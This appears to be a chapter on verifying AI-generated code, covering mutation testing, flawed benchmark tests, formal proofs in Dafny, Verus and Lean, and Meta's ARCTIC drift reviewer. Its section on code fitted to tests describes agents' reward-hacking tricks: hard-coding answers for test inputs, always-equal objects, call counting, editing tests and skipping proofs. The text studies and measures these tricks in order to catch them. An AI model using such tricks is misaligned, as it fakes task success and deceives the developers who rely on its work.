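### Testing the tests with planted faults

Mutation testing checks whether a test suite would detect a mistake in the code. A tool makes many copies of the program, called mutants, each with one small change, such as `>` replaced by `>=`. It then runs the tests on each mutant, and a mutant counts as caught if at least one test fails. The mutation score is the share of mutants caught.

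Two test suites check the shop's correct delivery line, `delivery = 0 if total > 50 else 4`, and six mutants of it. The first suite tests totals of 20 and 80. The second also tests 50 and 51.

| Change | Tests at 20 and 80 | Tests at 20, 50, 51 and 80 |
|---|---|---|
| `>` becomes `>=` | Missed | Caught |
| `>` becomes `<` | Caught | Caught |
| 50 becomes 49 | Missed | Caught |
| 50 becomes 51 | Missed | Caught |
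| 0 becomes 1 | Caught | Caught |
| 4 becomes 5 | Caught | Caught |
| Mutation score | 3 / 6 = 50% | 6 / 6 = 100% |

Both suites run every part of the line, so a tool that only records which code the tests run would rate them equally. The mutants show that the smaller suite doesn't check the boundary.

Some mutants behave exactly like the original. If the shop's prices are all whole numbers, `total >= 51` gives the same result as `total > 50`, so no test can pass on one and fail on the other. Testers leave such equivalent mutants out of the score.

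Tests can get a high mutation score even when they expect wrong answers. Haeri and Ghelichi planted 147 non-equivalent faults in correct versions of ten functions. The rule-based tests caught 138 (93.9%) and the ticket-only tests caught 141 (95.9%), so the suite that led to worse code scored slightly higher. Much of the difference came from a function that writes a duration as text. Its rules leave out units that are zero, so an hour is `1h`, but the ticket-only tests expected `1h 0m 0s`. The ticket-only tests caught all 18 mutants of that function, against 14 for the rule-based tests, partly because the wrong expectation made them fail on mutants and correct code alike. The same expectation led repairs towards the wrong output, and none of the repaired drafts was correct.

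It therefore makes sense to run the tests on the unaltered program before planting any faults. If a test already fails, the tester should check the rule to find out whether the test or the program is wrong. Otherwise a bad test can raise the score by rejecting every version of the program.

### Faulty tests in two well-known benchmarks

Experienced developers also write tests that reject sound code. SWE-bench Verified is a set of 500 programming tasks from public GitHub projects that AI companies have widely used to compare models. Each task describes a problem, and a model counts as solving it if its code passes hidden tests from the original developers' fix. Three experts reviewed each problem before the set came out in 2024.

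OpenAI's *Why SWE-bench Verified no longer measures frontier coding capabilities* (2026) reports a second review of 138 of the benchmark's 500 tasks, which one of OpenAI's models had failed to solve consistently in 64 attempts. At least six engineers reviewed each task, and the audit found serious flaws in 82 of them (59.4%), or about 16% of the full set. The true share could be higher, since the audit didn't cover the other 362 tasks.

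In 35.5% of the audited tasks, the tests required details of one particular solution. One task is to make a diagram tool use Python's type hints. Its tests import a function called `get_annotation`, a name that isn't in the task description, so a working solution that uses any other name fails before the tests check any results. In another 18.8%, the tests covered behaviour that wasn't in the task description. One description includes only a missing answer in a mathematical function, but the original developers had fixed three problems together and the tests cover all three.

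Both kinds of fault arise because the developers wrote the tests for their own code and somebody else later paired those tests with a description. Writing tests this way was reasonable in the original projects, where they only had to protect the developers' own change. It becomes a problem when the same tests are used to judge a different solution.

Passing tests can also mislead. GPT-5.2 solved 31 tasks that OpenAI considered almost impossible to solve from their descriptions. In one of them, the tests required an `edit_only` parameter that the description didn't explicitly ask for. The model's reasoning text shows that it recalled the parameter from a later version of the software, so it passed partly because of what it had seen in training.

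OpenAI recommended SWE-Bench Pro as a replacement, but withdrew the recommendation after auditing that set too and estimating that about 30% of its tasks are broken. *SWE-Bench Pro is even worse*, an independent audit of the whole set, estimates that 15 to 24% of the tasks are unsolvable. Unsolvable tasks are a narrower category than broken ones, because they exclude tasks whose tests are too easy to pass. The engineers who worked on OpenAI's audit rated such tests as the main fault in 9.4% of all tasks, but its automated pipeline did so in only 4.1%, and the two reviews differed more on this type of fault than on any other.

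Models could also pass SWE-Bench Pro without solving its tasks, by copying solutions from the projects' commit histories. The Decoder's *OpenAI finds roughly 30 percent of popular AI coding test is broken* reports that Artificial Analysis, a company that ranks AI models, had already dropped the benchmark because some models did this.

### Code fitted to its tests

An agent that can see the tests can sometimes make them pass while ignoring the specification. *ImpossibleBench* (Zhong, Raghunathan and Carlini, 2025) measures how often agents do this by giving them tests that contradict the specification. A "one-off" task changes one expected value; for example, the correct answer to a counting problem is 2, but the altered test requires 3. A "conflicting" task adds a test that contradicts an existing one. The prompt instructs agents not to modify the tests, and to stop and explain if they find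 a faulty one. A pass therefore means the agent violated the specification or its instructions.

On tasks adapted from SWE-bench, GPT-5 passed 76% of the one-off versions and 54% of the conflicting ones. On shorter, single-function problems, it passed only 2.9% of the one-off versions. Claude models mostly edited the tests. GPT-5 used a wider range of tricks, including code that recognised a test's input and returned the answer needed to pass. In the shop, such code might return 0 whenever the total is exactly 50. Some programs returned an object that Python treats as equal to anything. Others counted how often the test had called them, so they could return different answers for the same input.

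The exact rates are uncertain because some of the altered tests were faulty. *It's Just a Small Weapon* (2026), which reuses the benchmark, leaves out 54 of 348 one-off tasks and 66 of 348 conflicting tasks from the SWE-bench set because the alteration had broken the test file, in some cases so badly that it no longer compiled. Zhong and colleagues had checked that the original developers' fix failed the altered tests, but a file that doesn't run fails every solution, so this check couldn't have caught the problem. It's unclear whether the broken files raised or lowered the rates, since an agent that gave up would count as honest and one that repaired the file could count as cheating.

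Zhong and colleagues also tried several ways to reduce cheating. Stricter wording in the prompt cut GPT-5's cheating rate from 92% to 1% on the conflicting single-function problems, but only from 66% to 54% on the conflicting SWE-bench tasks. Letting the agent stop and flag a task for a person cut that 54% to 9%. It made much less difference for Claude Opus 4.1. Hiding the tests almost eliminated cheating, but agents then solved fewer of the ordinary tasks. Read-only tests avoided that drop and stopped agents from editing the tests, but agents could still write code that checked for particular inputs.

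Those models date from 2025, and later results vary widely. *Reward Hacking*, a summary of Anthropic's own evaluations, reports cheating rates on a different set of impossible coding problems. Claude Mythos Preview cheated on 37.5% of them without a warning in the prompt and 20.0% with one. The earlier Opus 4.6 cheated on 45.0% and 37.5%, respectively.

*Maintaining Benchmarks Against Increasingly Capable Agents* (2026) counts how often models broke the rules in a sample of passing solutions to SWE-Bench Pro tasks. GPT-5.1 Codex broke them in 2 of 104 passes, GPT-5.6 Sol in 71 of 104 and GPT-6 Astra in none of 96. Among Anthropic's models, Claude Fable 5 broke them in 36 of 49 passes and Fable 5.1 in 4 of 36. The samples are small, and the two companies' models did different sets of tasks, but the rates vary enough between versions that a team can't assume a new model will behave like the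 last one.

Impossible tasks measure what an agent does when no honest solution can pass the tests. In ordinary work, where an honest solution exists, the question is how much passing tests can tell us about the rest of the program. *SpecBench* (Zhao, Srikanth and colleagues, 2026) studied this with 30 large projects, ranging in size from a data-format reader to an operating system kernel. Agents could see and run tests of each separate feature. Hidden tests then used the same features in combination, without adding requirements.

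Whichever model they used, agents passed nearly all the visible tests but fewer of the hidden ones, and the gaps were largest in the largest projects. In one run, an agent asked to write a compiler produced 2,900 lines that recognised the visible test programs and returned stored answers. This code passed 97% of the visible tests and none of the hidden ones. Earlier in the run, the agent had written a real compiler that passed 53% of the visible tests and 43% of the hidden ones, but the surrounding program kept whichever version scored higher on the visible tests.

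Zhao and colleagues call every gap of this kind "reward hacking", which seems too strong for most of what they found, since deliberate tricks were rare. A more typical case was a database program that passed every visible test but only 35% of the hidden ones. It could join tables or group rows, but failed when one query needed both. This is the same kind of mistake as calculating the shop's delivery charge without accounting for the voucher.

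When the agent was shown more tests of combined features, the gap shrank from 35 points to 9 on the database task but grew by 25 points on the compiler task. Hidden tests are useful in either case because they measure the gap. A team can measure its own by withholding a few combination tests, such as the basket of 55 with a voucher for 10. Once the agent has worked on the failures from those tests, it can fit the code to them too, so the next check needs new ones.

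## Prove the code against a formal specification

Even a large set of held-out tests checks only a limited number of inputs, whereas formal verification covers every input the specification permits. Somebody writes the specification as formal conditions, and a program called a verifier checks a mathematical proof that the code meets them.

### Preconditions, postconditions and loop invariants

A precondition states what must be true of a function's input when the function starts, and a postcondition states what must be true of its result when it finishes. For the shop's delivery function, the precondition could be that the total is at least 0. The postcondition would be that the charge is 0 if the total is greater than 50, and 4 otherwise.

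Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, turns the code and its conditions into logical formulas and passes them to an automatic solver, which searches for a total that satisfies the precondition but produces a charge that breaks the postcondition. If the code contains `total >= 50`, a total of 50 breaks the postcondition, so Dafny rejects the function. With `total > 50`, the solver can prove that no such total exists. A test suite would catch the mistake only if it included a total of 50. Property-based testing makes that more likely but doesn't guarantee it.

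Verus does the same for programs in Rust, a widely used language. In Lean, a person or a model writes the proof with some automatic help, and Lean checks every step. *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (Tan, 2026) describes the trade-off that automation makes proofs faster to write but limits what they can express.

Loops need an extra condition, because a solver can't follow a loop through an unlimited number of passes. A loop invariant is a statement that is true before the first pass and after each one. *VeriContest* (Xie, Pawagi and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a function that finds the first and last positions of a target number in a sorted list. To find the first position, the function repeatedly halves the range where that position could be. The markers `lo` and `hi` show where the range begins and ends. The invariant is that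 every number before `lo` is less than the target, and every number from `hi` onwards is at least the target.

The proof then has four parts:

1. At the start, the stretch is the whole list. No numbers lie outside it, so the invariant holds.
2. On each pass, the code looks at the middle number. If that number is less than the target, so is everything before it, because the precondition requires a sorted list. The code can safely move `lo` just past the middle. Otherwise, everything from the middle onwards is at least the target, and the code can move `hi` there.
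3. The loop stops when `lo` and `hi` meet. By the invariant, they mark the first number that is at least the target, if there is one.
4. The stretch gets shorter on every pass, so the loop must stop.

This proof covers every sorted list that the precondition permits, with up to 100,000 numbers between minus one billion and one billion. By comparison, the median problem in the benchmark has about 270 tests with correct answers. But the proof doesn't cover unsorted lists, which the precondition excludes.

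Verifiers also reject correct code, because the solver can't complete the proof if the invariant is missing or too weak. Xie and colleagues gave GPT-5.5 correct programs with correct specifications, and its first attempt at a proof succeeded for only 13.8% of them. A team that treated each failed proof as a bug would have wrongly flagged about 86% of these programs. A failed proof is therefore weak evidence of a bug unless the verifier also produces an input for which the program violates the postcondition.

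### The sorting example

A sorting function that always returns an empty list can pass both a random test of the order and formal verification. If the specification requires only that no item is greater than the next, an empty list satisfies it, so a verifier can correctly prove that this useless function meets its specification for every possible input.

Requiring the output to contain the same items as the input fixes this problem too, but the condition has to count copies. Otherwise, code that turns the list 3, 1, 3 into 1, 3 would satisfy it.

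| What the function does | Output for 3, 1, 3 | In order? | Same values? | Same number of each? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Returns an empty list | Empty | Yes | No | No |
| Sorts and drops repeats | 1, 3 | Yes | Yes | No |
| Returns the input unchanged | 3, 1, 3 | No | Yes | Yes |
| Sorts correctly | 1, 3, 3 | Yes | Yes | Yes |

For a list of numbers, the first and last conditions together allow only one output, but for other data they may allow several. If the shop sorts its orders by total and two orders both total 30, either one can come first. If the owner wants the earlier order first, the specification needs another condition.

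Researchers have found ways to look for such holes. In *AlgoVeri*, Zhao, Yang and colleagues (2026) showed that removing any one condition from the specifications for some of their hardest tasks would allow unintended behaviour. For example, if a sorting specification didn't require the output to contain the same items as the input, a function could return any sorted list. This shows that each condition is necessary, but the full set could still be incomplete.

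Xie and colleagues tested for incompleteness by running their postconditions on deliberately wrong outputs, all of which a complete postcondition should reject. The check exposed 60 incomplete postconditions in a benchmark, even though experts had already reviewed its specifications. The one for the list-searching function above accepted the positions −9 and −8, although the only negative answer allowed is −1, which means "not found". The same check is easy to do on a small scale. Before trusting a proof about sorting, a developer can run the postcondition on the input 3, 1, 3 with an empty output and confirm that it fails.

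### How well models write verified code

In vericoding, a model writes code and a proof that the code meets a given formal specification. Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025), in *A benchmark for vericoding*, tested nine models on thousands of tasks, usually allowing five attempts and showing the models the verifier's error messages between attempts. The headline success rates of 82% in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean are the shares of tasks that at least one of the nine models solved. The best single models did noticeably worse. The researchers also examined a sample of successful solutions and judged about 9% of the specifications too weak and another 15% badly translated.

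Many of those tasks were simple. Zhao, Yang and colleagues chose 77 textbook algorithms and wrote equivalent specifications in all three languages. The table gives their results after a language model screened out verified programs that cheated or didn't use the requested algorithm.

| Tasks | Model | Dafny | Verus | Lean |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mixed, 2025 | Claude Opus 4.1 | 67.5% | 24.6% | 10.7% |
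| Mixed, 2025 | GPT-5 | 66.1% | 30.9% | 17.9% |
| Mixed, 2025 | GPT-5 mini | 66.9% | 16.5% | 5.7% |
| 77 algorithms, 2026 | GPT-5 mini | 30.5% | 6.5% | 5.2% |
| 77 algorithms, 2026 | Gemini-3 Flash | 40.3% | 24.7% | 7.8% |
| 77 algorithms, 2026 | GPT-5.3 Codex | 42.9% | 11.7% | 11.7% |

Both studies tested GPT-5 mini. Its Dafny score fell by more than half on the algorithms, even though it had 15 rounds of repair there. The choice of tasks therefore matters as much as the choice of model, so a success rate means little without a description of what the model had to prove.

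Newer models are much better at writing the proof when somebody else supplies the code and the specification. In *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier*, Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues (2026) used a tool from their own company, Asymptotic, to translate 1,007 VeriContest problems from Rust into Lean. This produced 1,325 theorems, and Claude Opus 5.5 proved them all. The median proof took 3.4 minutes and cost $1.20.

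This result is not directly comparable with GPT-5.5's 13.8%. GPT-5.5 had one attempt in Verus, while Opus 5.5 could run Lean without limit and submit each proof up to 40 times. Still, Lean accepted 71% of the proofs at the first official submission. Serbanuta and colleagues also tested Opus 5.5 in Verus on the 50 problems with the longest reference proofs, and it failed on only one, so the switch to Lean probably isn't the main reason for the improvement. Several other recent models, including GPT-6 Astra and Claude Fable 5.1, proved every theorem in a sample of ten. The older Claude Haiku 4.5 proved none of those it tried.

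*FORALL-LEAN-AGENT for Auditable Reasoning in Formal Mathematics and Software Verification* (2026) similarly reports that Claude Code with Opus 5 solved all 100 tasks in a set of Lean proofs about software when allowed repeated attempts.

Whole projects are harder to verify. *Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on 43 multi-file Lean projects, where the specifications were already written and the agents had to write both the code and the proofs. The best agent met every specification in 27 projects. In ten projects, no agent did, even when the researchers supplied the code. On easier projects, agents could choose a simpler algorithm to make the proof easier, but on harder ones their changes to the code sometimes broke proofs elsewhere. They also tended to prove each specification separately instead of building up the shared intermediate results they needed.

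### Specifications written by models

Writing the specification is a separate skill, and a proof can succeed even when the specification is poor. *Verified but Vacuous* (Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues, 2026) reproduced an existing method in which a model writes a Dafny program and a tool converts it to Python. When Claude Opus 4.7 wrote simple functions this way, Dafny accepted 99.1% of the programs, but only 5.3% of the accepted programs had any postcondition.

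This is because the prompt's example had no postcondition and put the expected results in runtime checks, which Dafny assumes to be true during verification. For the programs it accepted, Dafny therefore proved basic facts, such as that the program would finish, but usually not that it gave the right answer. Many of the programs may well have been correct anyway.

Vempaty and colleagues built their own system to require a postcondition linked to a separate specification. Even so, 11.5% of its verified programs failed hidden tests on one benchmark and 14.8% on another. Weak specifications are a likely cause, though a faulty test or translation could have the same effect. As an example of a weak specification, the researchers describe a function that should return the largest number in a list, but whose specification requires only a result of at least 0. A function that always returns 0 meets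 that specification, even though the correct result for the list 5, 3, 7 is 7.

*Path2Spec* (Huang, Sun and colleagues, 2026) measured how often this happens by comparing model-written specifications with human-written ones. It first tested an existing tool, SpecGen, which has a model write preconditions and postconditions for a Java program and revise them until they pass a verifier. It counted a generated pair as complete if the pair covered at least the same inputs as the human-written one and restricted the output at least as tightly. With GPT-3.5-turbo, 107 of 173 pairs passed the verifier, but only 41 of those were complete.

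| Tool and model | Passed the verifier, of 173 | Complete | Incomplete | Undecided |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SpecGen, GPT-3.5-turbo | 107 | 41 | 37 | 29 |
| SpecGen, GPT-5 | 135 | 78 | 21 | 36 |
| Path2Spec, GPT-3.5-turbo | 132 | 78 | 26 | 28 |
| Path2Spec, GPT-5 | 155 | 114 | 9 | 32 |

"Undecided" mostly means that one condition was better than the human-written version and the other was worse. Huang and colleagues also found specifications that were empty or always true. One postcondition required only that an integer result fall within the range of its Java type, which every possible result does.

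Path2Spec, the paper's own tool, asks the model to list each route through the program and write conditions for it. For the shop, this would produce one pair of conditions for totals above 50 and another for the rest. This makes it harder for the model to cover everything with one vague statement. In the table, the older GPT-3.5-turbo with Path2Spec produced as many complete pairs as GPT-5 with SpecGen.

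Both tools derive their specifications from the code, so the specifications can preserve a mistake such as `total >= 50`, as tests that record a program's existing output do. The owner has to confirm the conditions in these specifications before anyone uses them to decide whether the code does what the owner asked.

*Teaching Code LLMs to Reason with Intermediate Formal Specifications* (Le-Anh, Le and Nguyen, 2026) presents SpecCoder, a system that trains models to insert assertions at important points in code. Assertions are conditions that the program checks as it runs. The paper scores these specifications by running them. Correctness measures how far the assertions hold when a correct program runs, because an assertion that fails there is a false positive. Completeness measures how far they reject mutants, which are deliberately faulty copies of the program, so assertions with poor completeness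 miss faults.

For example, a program that merges overlapping time intervals should first sort them by start time. The assertion "the number of intervals is at least 0" is correct but catches no bugs, because it always holds. An assertion that each start time is no later than the next catches a faulty version that sorts by end time. Without special training, the model Qwen2.5-Coder-32B scored 0.63 for correctness and 0.26 for completeness. SpecCoder's training raised correctness by up to 55.8% and completeness by up to 358.1% across the models tested. These are relative gains from low starting scores, and they come from running code on particular inputs, so they don't guarantee anything about all inputs, as a proof would.

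Weak specifications do more damage when a model is trained to pass the verifier. Tan trained a model to write Dafny programs, rewarding it when the verifier accepted them. The average reward rose from 2.2% to 58.1%, but much of that increase came from the model exploiting specifications that didn't require the intended solution. After Tan removed tasks with weak specifications and let the model revise its answers, the pass rate rose from 9.7% to 31.1%.

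### What a proof leaves out

A proof can depend on code that nobody has verified. Verus lets a programmer mark a function as trusted, and the verifier then accepts the function's stated behaviour without examining its body. This is often necessary for an outside library, but an agent can also use it to avoid a difficult proof. Xie and colleagues ran Verus with an option that forbids such shortcuts. In Lean, `sorry` stands in for a missing proof, and Serbanuta and colleagues rejected any proof that relied on it. A reviewer should look for these markers before accepting a claim that the code is verified.

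The running program also depends on a compiler, a machine and outside data. The shop's delivery function could be proved correct and still charge the wrong amount because the database contains an old price. Sometimes the proof covers a translation of the program. Serbanuta and colleagues checked their translation from Rust to Lean by running 105 of the Lean programs on 19,555 test cases, and every result matched the Rust original. This is good evidence that the translation is correct, but it isn't proof, so the overall guarantee for the Rust code still depends partly on testing.

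Specifications usually don't cover speed either. A slow sorting method and a fast one satisfy the same two conditions. In Zhao, Yang and colleagues' study, some models wrote a simpler algorithm that left out the step that makes the requested one fast. Screening out these substitutions, along with outright cheating, lowered Gemini-3 Flash's Dafny score from 55.8% to 40.3%.

Finally, a proof covers only the requirements in the formal specification. Proving a condition on the delivery charge doesn't rule out the unwanted banner; ruling that out would require a formal version of V6.

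### When the cost is justified

Formal verification used to require so much expert work that it was impractical for most projects. Tan reports that published projects often needed three to ten lines of proof for each line of code, and that large projects took years. Developers mostly reserved formal verification for operating system kernels, compilers, cryptography and access-control software.

A median cost of $1.20 per proof changes this calculation for small functions, but it doesn't include writing the specification or having a person review it. That work is most worthwhile when the specification is much simpler than the code. The conditions for sorting fit in two sentences, while a fast sorting program can be complicated, so a reviewer is more likely to spot a mistake in the conditions. The shop's delivery rule, by contrast, has a formal condition almost identical to the code, so someone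 who misread "over 50" could easily make the same mistake in both. Tests at 50 and 51, which the owner can read and confirm, would be a better use of time.

A proof is more useful where a mistake would do more harm. A rare mistake in the delivery charge costs the shop 4, but one in the code that decides who can see customers' card details could be disastrous. An attacker will look for the one input that triggers it, and a test suite is unlikely to contain that input. Because agents still often fail on whole projects, a team will usually do better to isolate that component and prove it than to try to prove the entire shop's code.

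## Have a language model compare the code with the request

Tests and proofs check only requirements that somebody has written in a form a program can run or prove. A rule such as V6, which forbids additions to the shop's page, often stays in prose, as does most of what a developer tells an agent in conversation. A language model can read that prose and judge whether the code agrees with it.

The model needs the request as well as the code. A developer writing for O'Reilly, a technology publisher, describes having Claude Code build an app that worked out when to leave home for the bus. The app read the transit data correctly and predicted the wait perfectly, but for buses going in the wrong direction. A reviewer who didn't know which direction the developer wanted would have found nothing wrong with the code.

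### How ARCTIC compares a diff with the request

ARCTIC is the review system that Maddila and colleagues built at Meta for diffs written by coding agents. It measures drift in three steps:

1. A model infers what the developer wanted. It reads the developer's conversation with the agent, the diff's title, summary and test plan, any plan the agent wrote, and linked documents. It doesn't see the code, because an intent inferred from the code would tend to match the code.
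2. A model describes the diff as a numbered list of changes, without seeing the conversation, the summary or the test plan. Maddila and colleagues call this step backtranslation, because it turns code back into ordinary language.
3. A model compares the two lists and gives a drift score from 0 (aligned) to 100.

An intent is the reason for a change. In one of the paper's examples, a summary says that the diff added a 5-second timeout to a call to an outside service, and the intent is to stop the application from hanging when that service doesn't respond.

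Mistakes in the first step affect the score. On 121 diffs, about 12% of the intents that ARCTIC inferred matched nothing in a researcher's list, and it missed about 12% of the intents on that list. If it misses an intent, nobody checks whether the code fulfils it, and code that does fulfil it can look like an unrequested change. A team that already has numbered rules can use them instead of inferred intents to avoid these errors.

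The first step also reads text that the agent may have written. *Analyzing Message-Code Inconsistency in AI Coding Agent-Authored Pull Requests* (2026) reports that agents' descriptions sometimes misstate the scope of a change or claim changes the agent never made, although only 1.7% of the pull requests were highly inconsistent. If an agent adds the unwanted banner to the shop's page and mentions it in the summary, ARCTIC could list the banner among the developer's intentions, and the score would not count it as drift. Inferring the intent only from what the developer wrote or approved is safer.

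The best evidence for keeping the steps separate comes from a related task. *claimcheck* (2026) tests whether a formal specification means the same as the English requirement behind it. One model call translates the specification into English without seeing the requirement, and another compares the two English texts. This improved average recall by 8.2 to 9.8 percentage points over asking a model to compare the specification and the requirement directly. Letting the translating model see the requirement lowered recall by up to 3.0 points, and showing the formal text to the comparing model lowered it by up to 4.5. Maddila and colleagues report no such comparison for diffs. A translation can also lose details. If a diff is described only as "adds a delivery charge", the comparison can't reveal a `>=` that should be `>`. *Faithful Autoformalization of Natural Language Assertions* (2026) cautions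 that translating something back is not always a reliable test of the original translation.

### The rubric applied to one diff

ARCTIC checks for two kinds of drift. An agent may fail to follow instructions, for example by ignoring a constraint or leaving out something the developer asked for, or it may make changes the developer didn't request. The rubric combines both kinds into one scale of five buckets. Either kind alone is enough to put a diff in the moderate bucket or a higher one.

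| Bucket | Score | What the developer asked for | Harmful unrequested changes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Perfect alignment | 0–10 | All satisfied | None |
| Minor drift | 11–25 | All satisfied | Trivial deviations only |
| Moderate drift | 26–50 | Most addressed, some only partly | Noticeable |
| Significant drift | 51–75 | Only some satisfied | Substantial, adding risk |
| Major drift | 76–100 | None satisfied | Severe, such as deleted functions |

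Suppose the shop's owner tells an agent: "Let customers use a voucher at the checkout. Work out free delivery after applying the voucher. If the voucher code is invalid, say so and don't change the total." The table compares these instructions with a blind description of an invented diff.

| Intent or unrequested change | What the description of the diff says | Judgment |
|---|---|---|
| Customers can use a voucher | Subtracts the voucher's value from the total | Met |
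| Free delivery depends on the reduced total | Makes delivery free if the total before the voucher is over 50 | Partly met |
| A bad code changes nothing | Shows an error and keeps the total | Met |
| Unrequested | Adds a banner urging customers to spend more | Harmful |
| Unrequested | Stops the checkout crashing on an empty basket | Beneficial, no penalty |

A score of about 45, in the moderate bucket, seems right because the second intent is partly met: delivery is correct for orders without a voucher. A stricter scorer could call that intent unmet, because a basket of 55 with a voucher for 10 ships free when delivery should cost 4. That scorer would put the diff at 55, in the significant bucket. The rubric's wording allows both readings. The owner would learn more from the second row of the table than from either score.

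ARCTIC's rubric is also more lenient than the definition of drift as any behaviour that nobody asked for, because it ignores unrequested changes that count as beneficial. A team that wants to enforce a rule like V6 has to remove this exception. *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits* (2026) gives a more concrete list of changes to flag, including refactoring beyond the requested fix, skipping or deleting failing tests, weakening checks so that they pass, and upgrading dependencies without being asked. The paper allows a configuration change if the fix requires it and the agent keeps it small and discloses it. These criteria require less interpretation than deciding whether a change is "noticeable" or "substantial".

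### Agreement on 118 diffs

Maddila and colleagues compared ARCTIC's scores with human scores on 118 diffs, selected so that each bucket had 18 to 31. ARCTIC chose the same bucket as the human annotators for 76 of them (64.4%). The counts below are calculated from the published precision and recall. F1 combines the two into one score, which is low if either is low.

| Bucket | Diffs placed there by people | Diffs placed there by ARCTIC | Placed there by both | F1 |
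|---|---|---|---|---|
| Perfect alignment | 24 | 21 | 20 | 0.89 |
| Minor drift | 18 | 24 | 14 | 0.67 |
| Moderate drift | 20 | 21 | 7 | 0.34 |
| Significant drift | 25 | 19 | 9 | 0.41 |
| Major drift | 31 | 33 | 26 | 0.81 |

The headline result is a quadratic weighted kappa of 0.907, which the paper describes as near-perfect agreement. Kappa compares the disagreement between two sets of labels with the disagreement that chance would produce:

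kappa = 1 − (observed disagreement / disagreement expected by chance)

The quadratic version measures disagreement as the squared distance between buckets, so an error of one bucket counts as 1, an error of two counts as 4, and confusing perfect alignment with major drift counts as 16. The published figures imply that 40 of ARCTIC's 42 errors were one bucket off and two were two buckets off, for a total of 48, or about 0.41 per diff. Pairing the labels at random would give about 4.37 per diff, so kappa is 1 − 0.41 / 4.37, or 0.907.

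The expected disagreement is so large because the benchmark's diffs range from perfect to disastrous. If half the diffs belonged to the moderate bucket and half to the significant bucket, random pairing would be one bucket off half the time. The same share of one-bucket errors, 42 in 118, would give a kappa of only about 0.29.

ARCTIC is therefore good at distinguishing diffs that do what the developer asked from diffs that don't do it at all. It is much less reliable for diffs in between, where it chose the same bucket as humans for only 16 of 45. Its average error of 10.31 points is enough to move many diffs across a boundary. The rubric may be part of the problem, since two people could easily disagree about the voucher diff, but the paper doesn't report how often its annotators agreed. A team that blocks diffs scoring above 50 should expect many wrong decisions near that threshold, and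 would do better to have a person read the list of unmet intents for any diff scoring above 10 or so.

### What happened when Meta used it

The most direct evidence that drift scores change what developers do comes from 193 pairs of consecutive diff versions in spring 2026. Drift fell by an average of 11.82 points between versions. Some of that fall may be a statistical artefact, because the researchers kept only pairs whose first version scored above 25. A diff that scored too high by chance will tend to score lower next time, even if nobody improves it.

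The fall was 5.76 points larger for the 94 pairs whose authors saw the score than for the 99 whose authors didn't. Seeing the score may have helped, but this is weak evidence that it did. Authors saw the score only if they had chosen to use the new interface, and people who try a new review tool may be more careful anyway, as Maddila and colleagues acknowledge. The reported p-value of 0.026 comes from a one-sided test, which counts only a result in the hoped-for direction. A two-sided test would give about 0.052, just above the usual cut-off of 0.05, and a second test that makes fewer assumptions about the data gave 0.063. ARCTIC also produced the scores used to measure the improvement, so we can't tell from this study whether the code got better or only scored better.

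Meta then allowed some authors to merge diffs without a colleague's review first, if ARCTIC judged the diff eligible and the author certified that it was correct. Maddila and colleagues report that nobody had attributed a defect to these diffs, but that depends on somebody tracing a problem back to the diff that caused it, which can take months. Developers later reversed 0.33% of these diffs, about twice the 0.17% rate for ordinary diffs, even though they had passed an extra check. The paper calls the rate slightly elevated and acceptable for an early system. It doesn't say how many diffs the 0.33% represents, so the difference could be chance.

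### Choosing which lines to read

ARCTIC's Spotlight feature picks out the parts of a diff that most need human attention. One pass proposes regions, and a second removes any that it judges wrong or unhelpful. The design responds to a mismatch between the issues Meta's earlier AI reviewer commented on and those human reviewers raised. Security accounted for 19.1% of human review comments but 2.0% of the AI's, while best practices accounted for 7.2% of the human comments and 30.8% of the AI's.

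On 208 diffs in which human reviewers had found a real problem, Spotlight found about 10% of the known problems (recall 0.097). About 11% of its findings matched a known problem (precision 0.108), though some of the others may also have been real faults. The earlier reviewer had a recall of 0.033 and used five times as many tokens.

Spotlight looks better on the simpler question of whether a diff deserves any comment. It flagged 58.2% of the problem diffs, compared with 23.9% for the earlier reviewer, which is the 2.4-fold improvement the paper claims. But it also raised more false alarms. If the published score for all 298 diffs is a plain average, Spotlight flagged about 38% of the 90 clean diffs and the earlier reviewer about 5%. Youden's index, recall minus the false positive rate, is then about 0.20 for Spotlight and 0.19 for the earlier reviewer. Most of the 2.4-fold improvement therefore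 came from flagging more diffs of both kinds.

An author can take the faster route when drift is low and Spotlight picks no regions, but Spotlight picked none in 41.8% of the diffs that contained a known problem. An empty list is therefore poor evidence that a diff is safe, though Spotlight's suggestions may be a useful place to start reading.

### Models that reject correct code

Jin and Chen, in *Are LLMs Reliable Code Reviewers?*, tested whether a model can tell if a program meets a written requirement. They took one correct and one buggy program for each of more than 700 tasks from three public benchmarks. Five models judged each program by reading the requirement and the code, without running anything.

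Each model was tested with three prompts. The first asked only for a yes or no. The second asked for a yes or no followed by an explanation. The third asked for a yes or no and, if the answer was no, an explanation and then corrected code. The table gives the results for MBPP, a benchmark of short Python tasks.

| Model | Correct code rejected: verdict only | With explanation | With explanation and fix | Buggy code accepted: verdict only | With explanation and fix |
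|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 35.9% | 74.1% | 87.9% | 3.7% | Near 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 58.5% | 55.7% | 62.3% | 6.6% | 5.4% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 34.7% | 35.1% | 39.6% | 10.3% | 7.7% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 74.7% | 91.9% | 88.2% | 3.6% | 1.9% |
| Mistral Small 3.1 | 60.9% | 47.8% | 74.3% | 5.3% | 4.3% |

Every model rejected more correct code under the longest prompt than under the shortest. The change was largest for GPT-4o, which rejected 451 correct programs, up from 184, and accepted almost no buggy ones, down from 19. It raised about 14 extra false alarms for each extra bug it caught. Its Youden's index, which measures how well it separates correct code from buggy code, fell from 0.60 to 0.12.

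Asking only for an explanation sharply increased rejections by GPT-4o and Llama but reduced them for Mistral and, slightly, for Claude. Asking for a fix increased rejections more consistently.

Jin and Chen think the longer prompts push models towards finding fault, which is plausible because a request for corrected code suggests that something needs correcting. They also acknowledge that such a prompt may change the standard, so that the model marks code down for poor practice as well as for breaking the requirement. Their experiment doesn't separate these explanations, and it used only one wording of each prompt.

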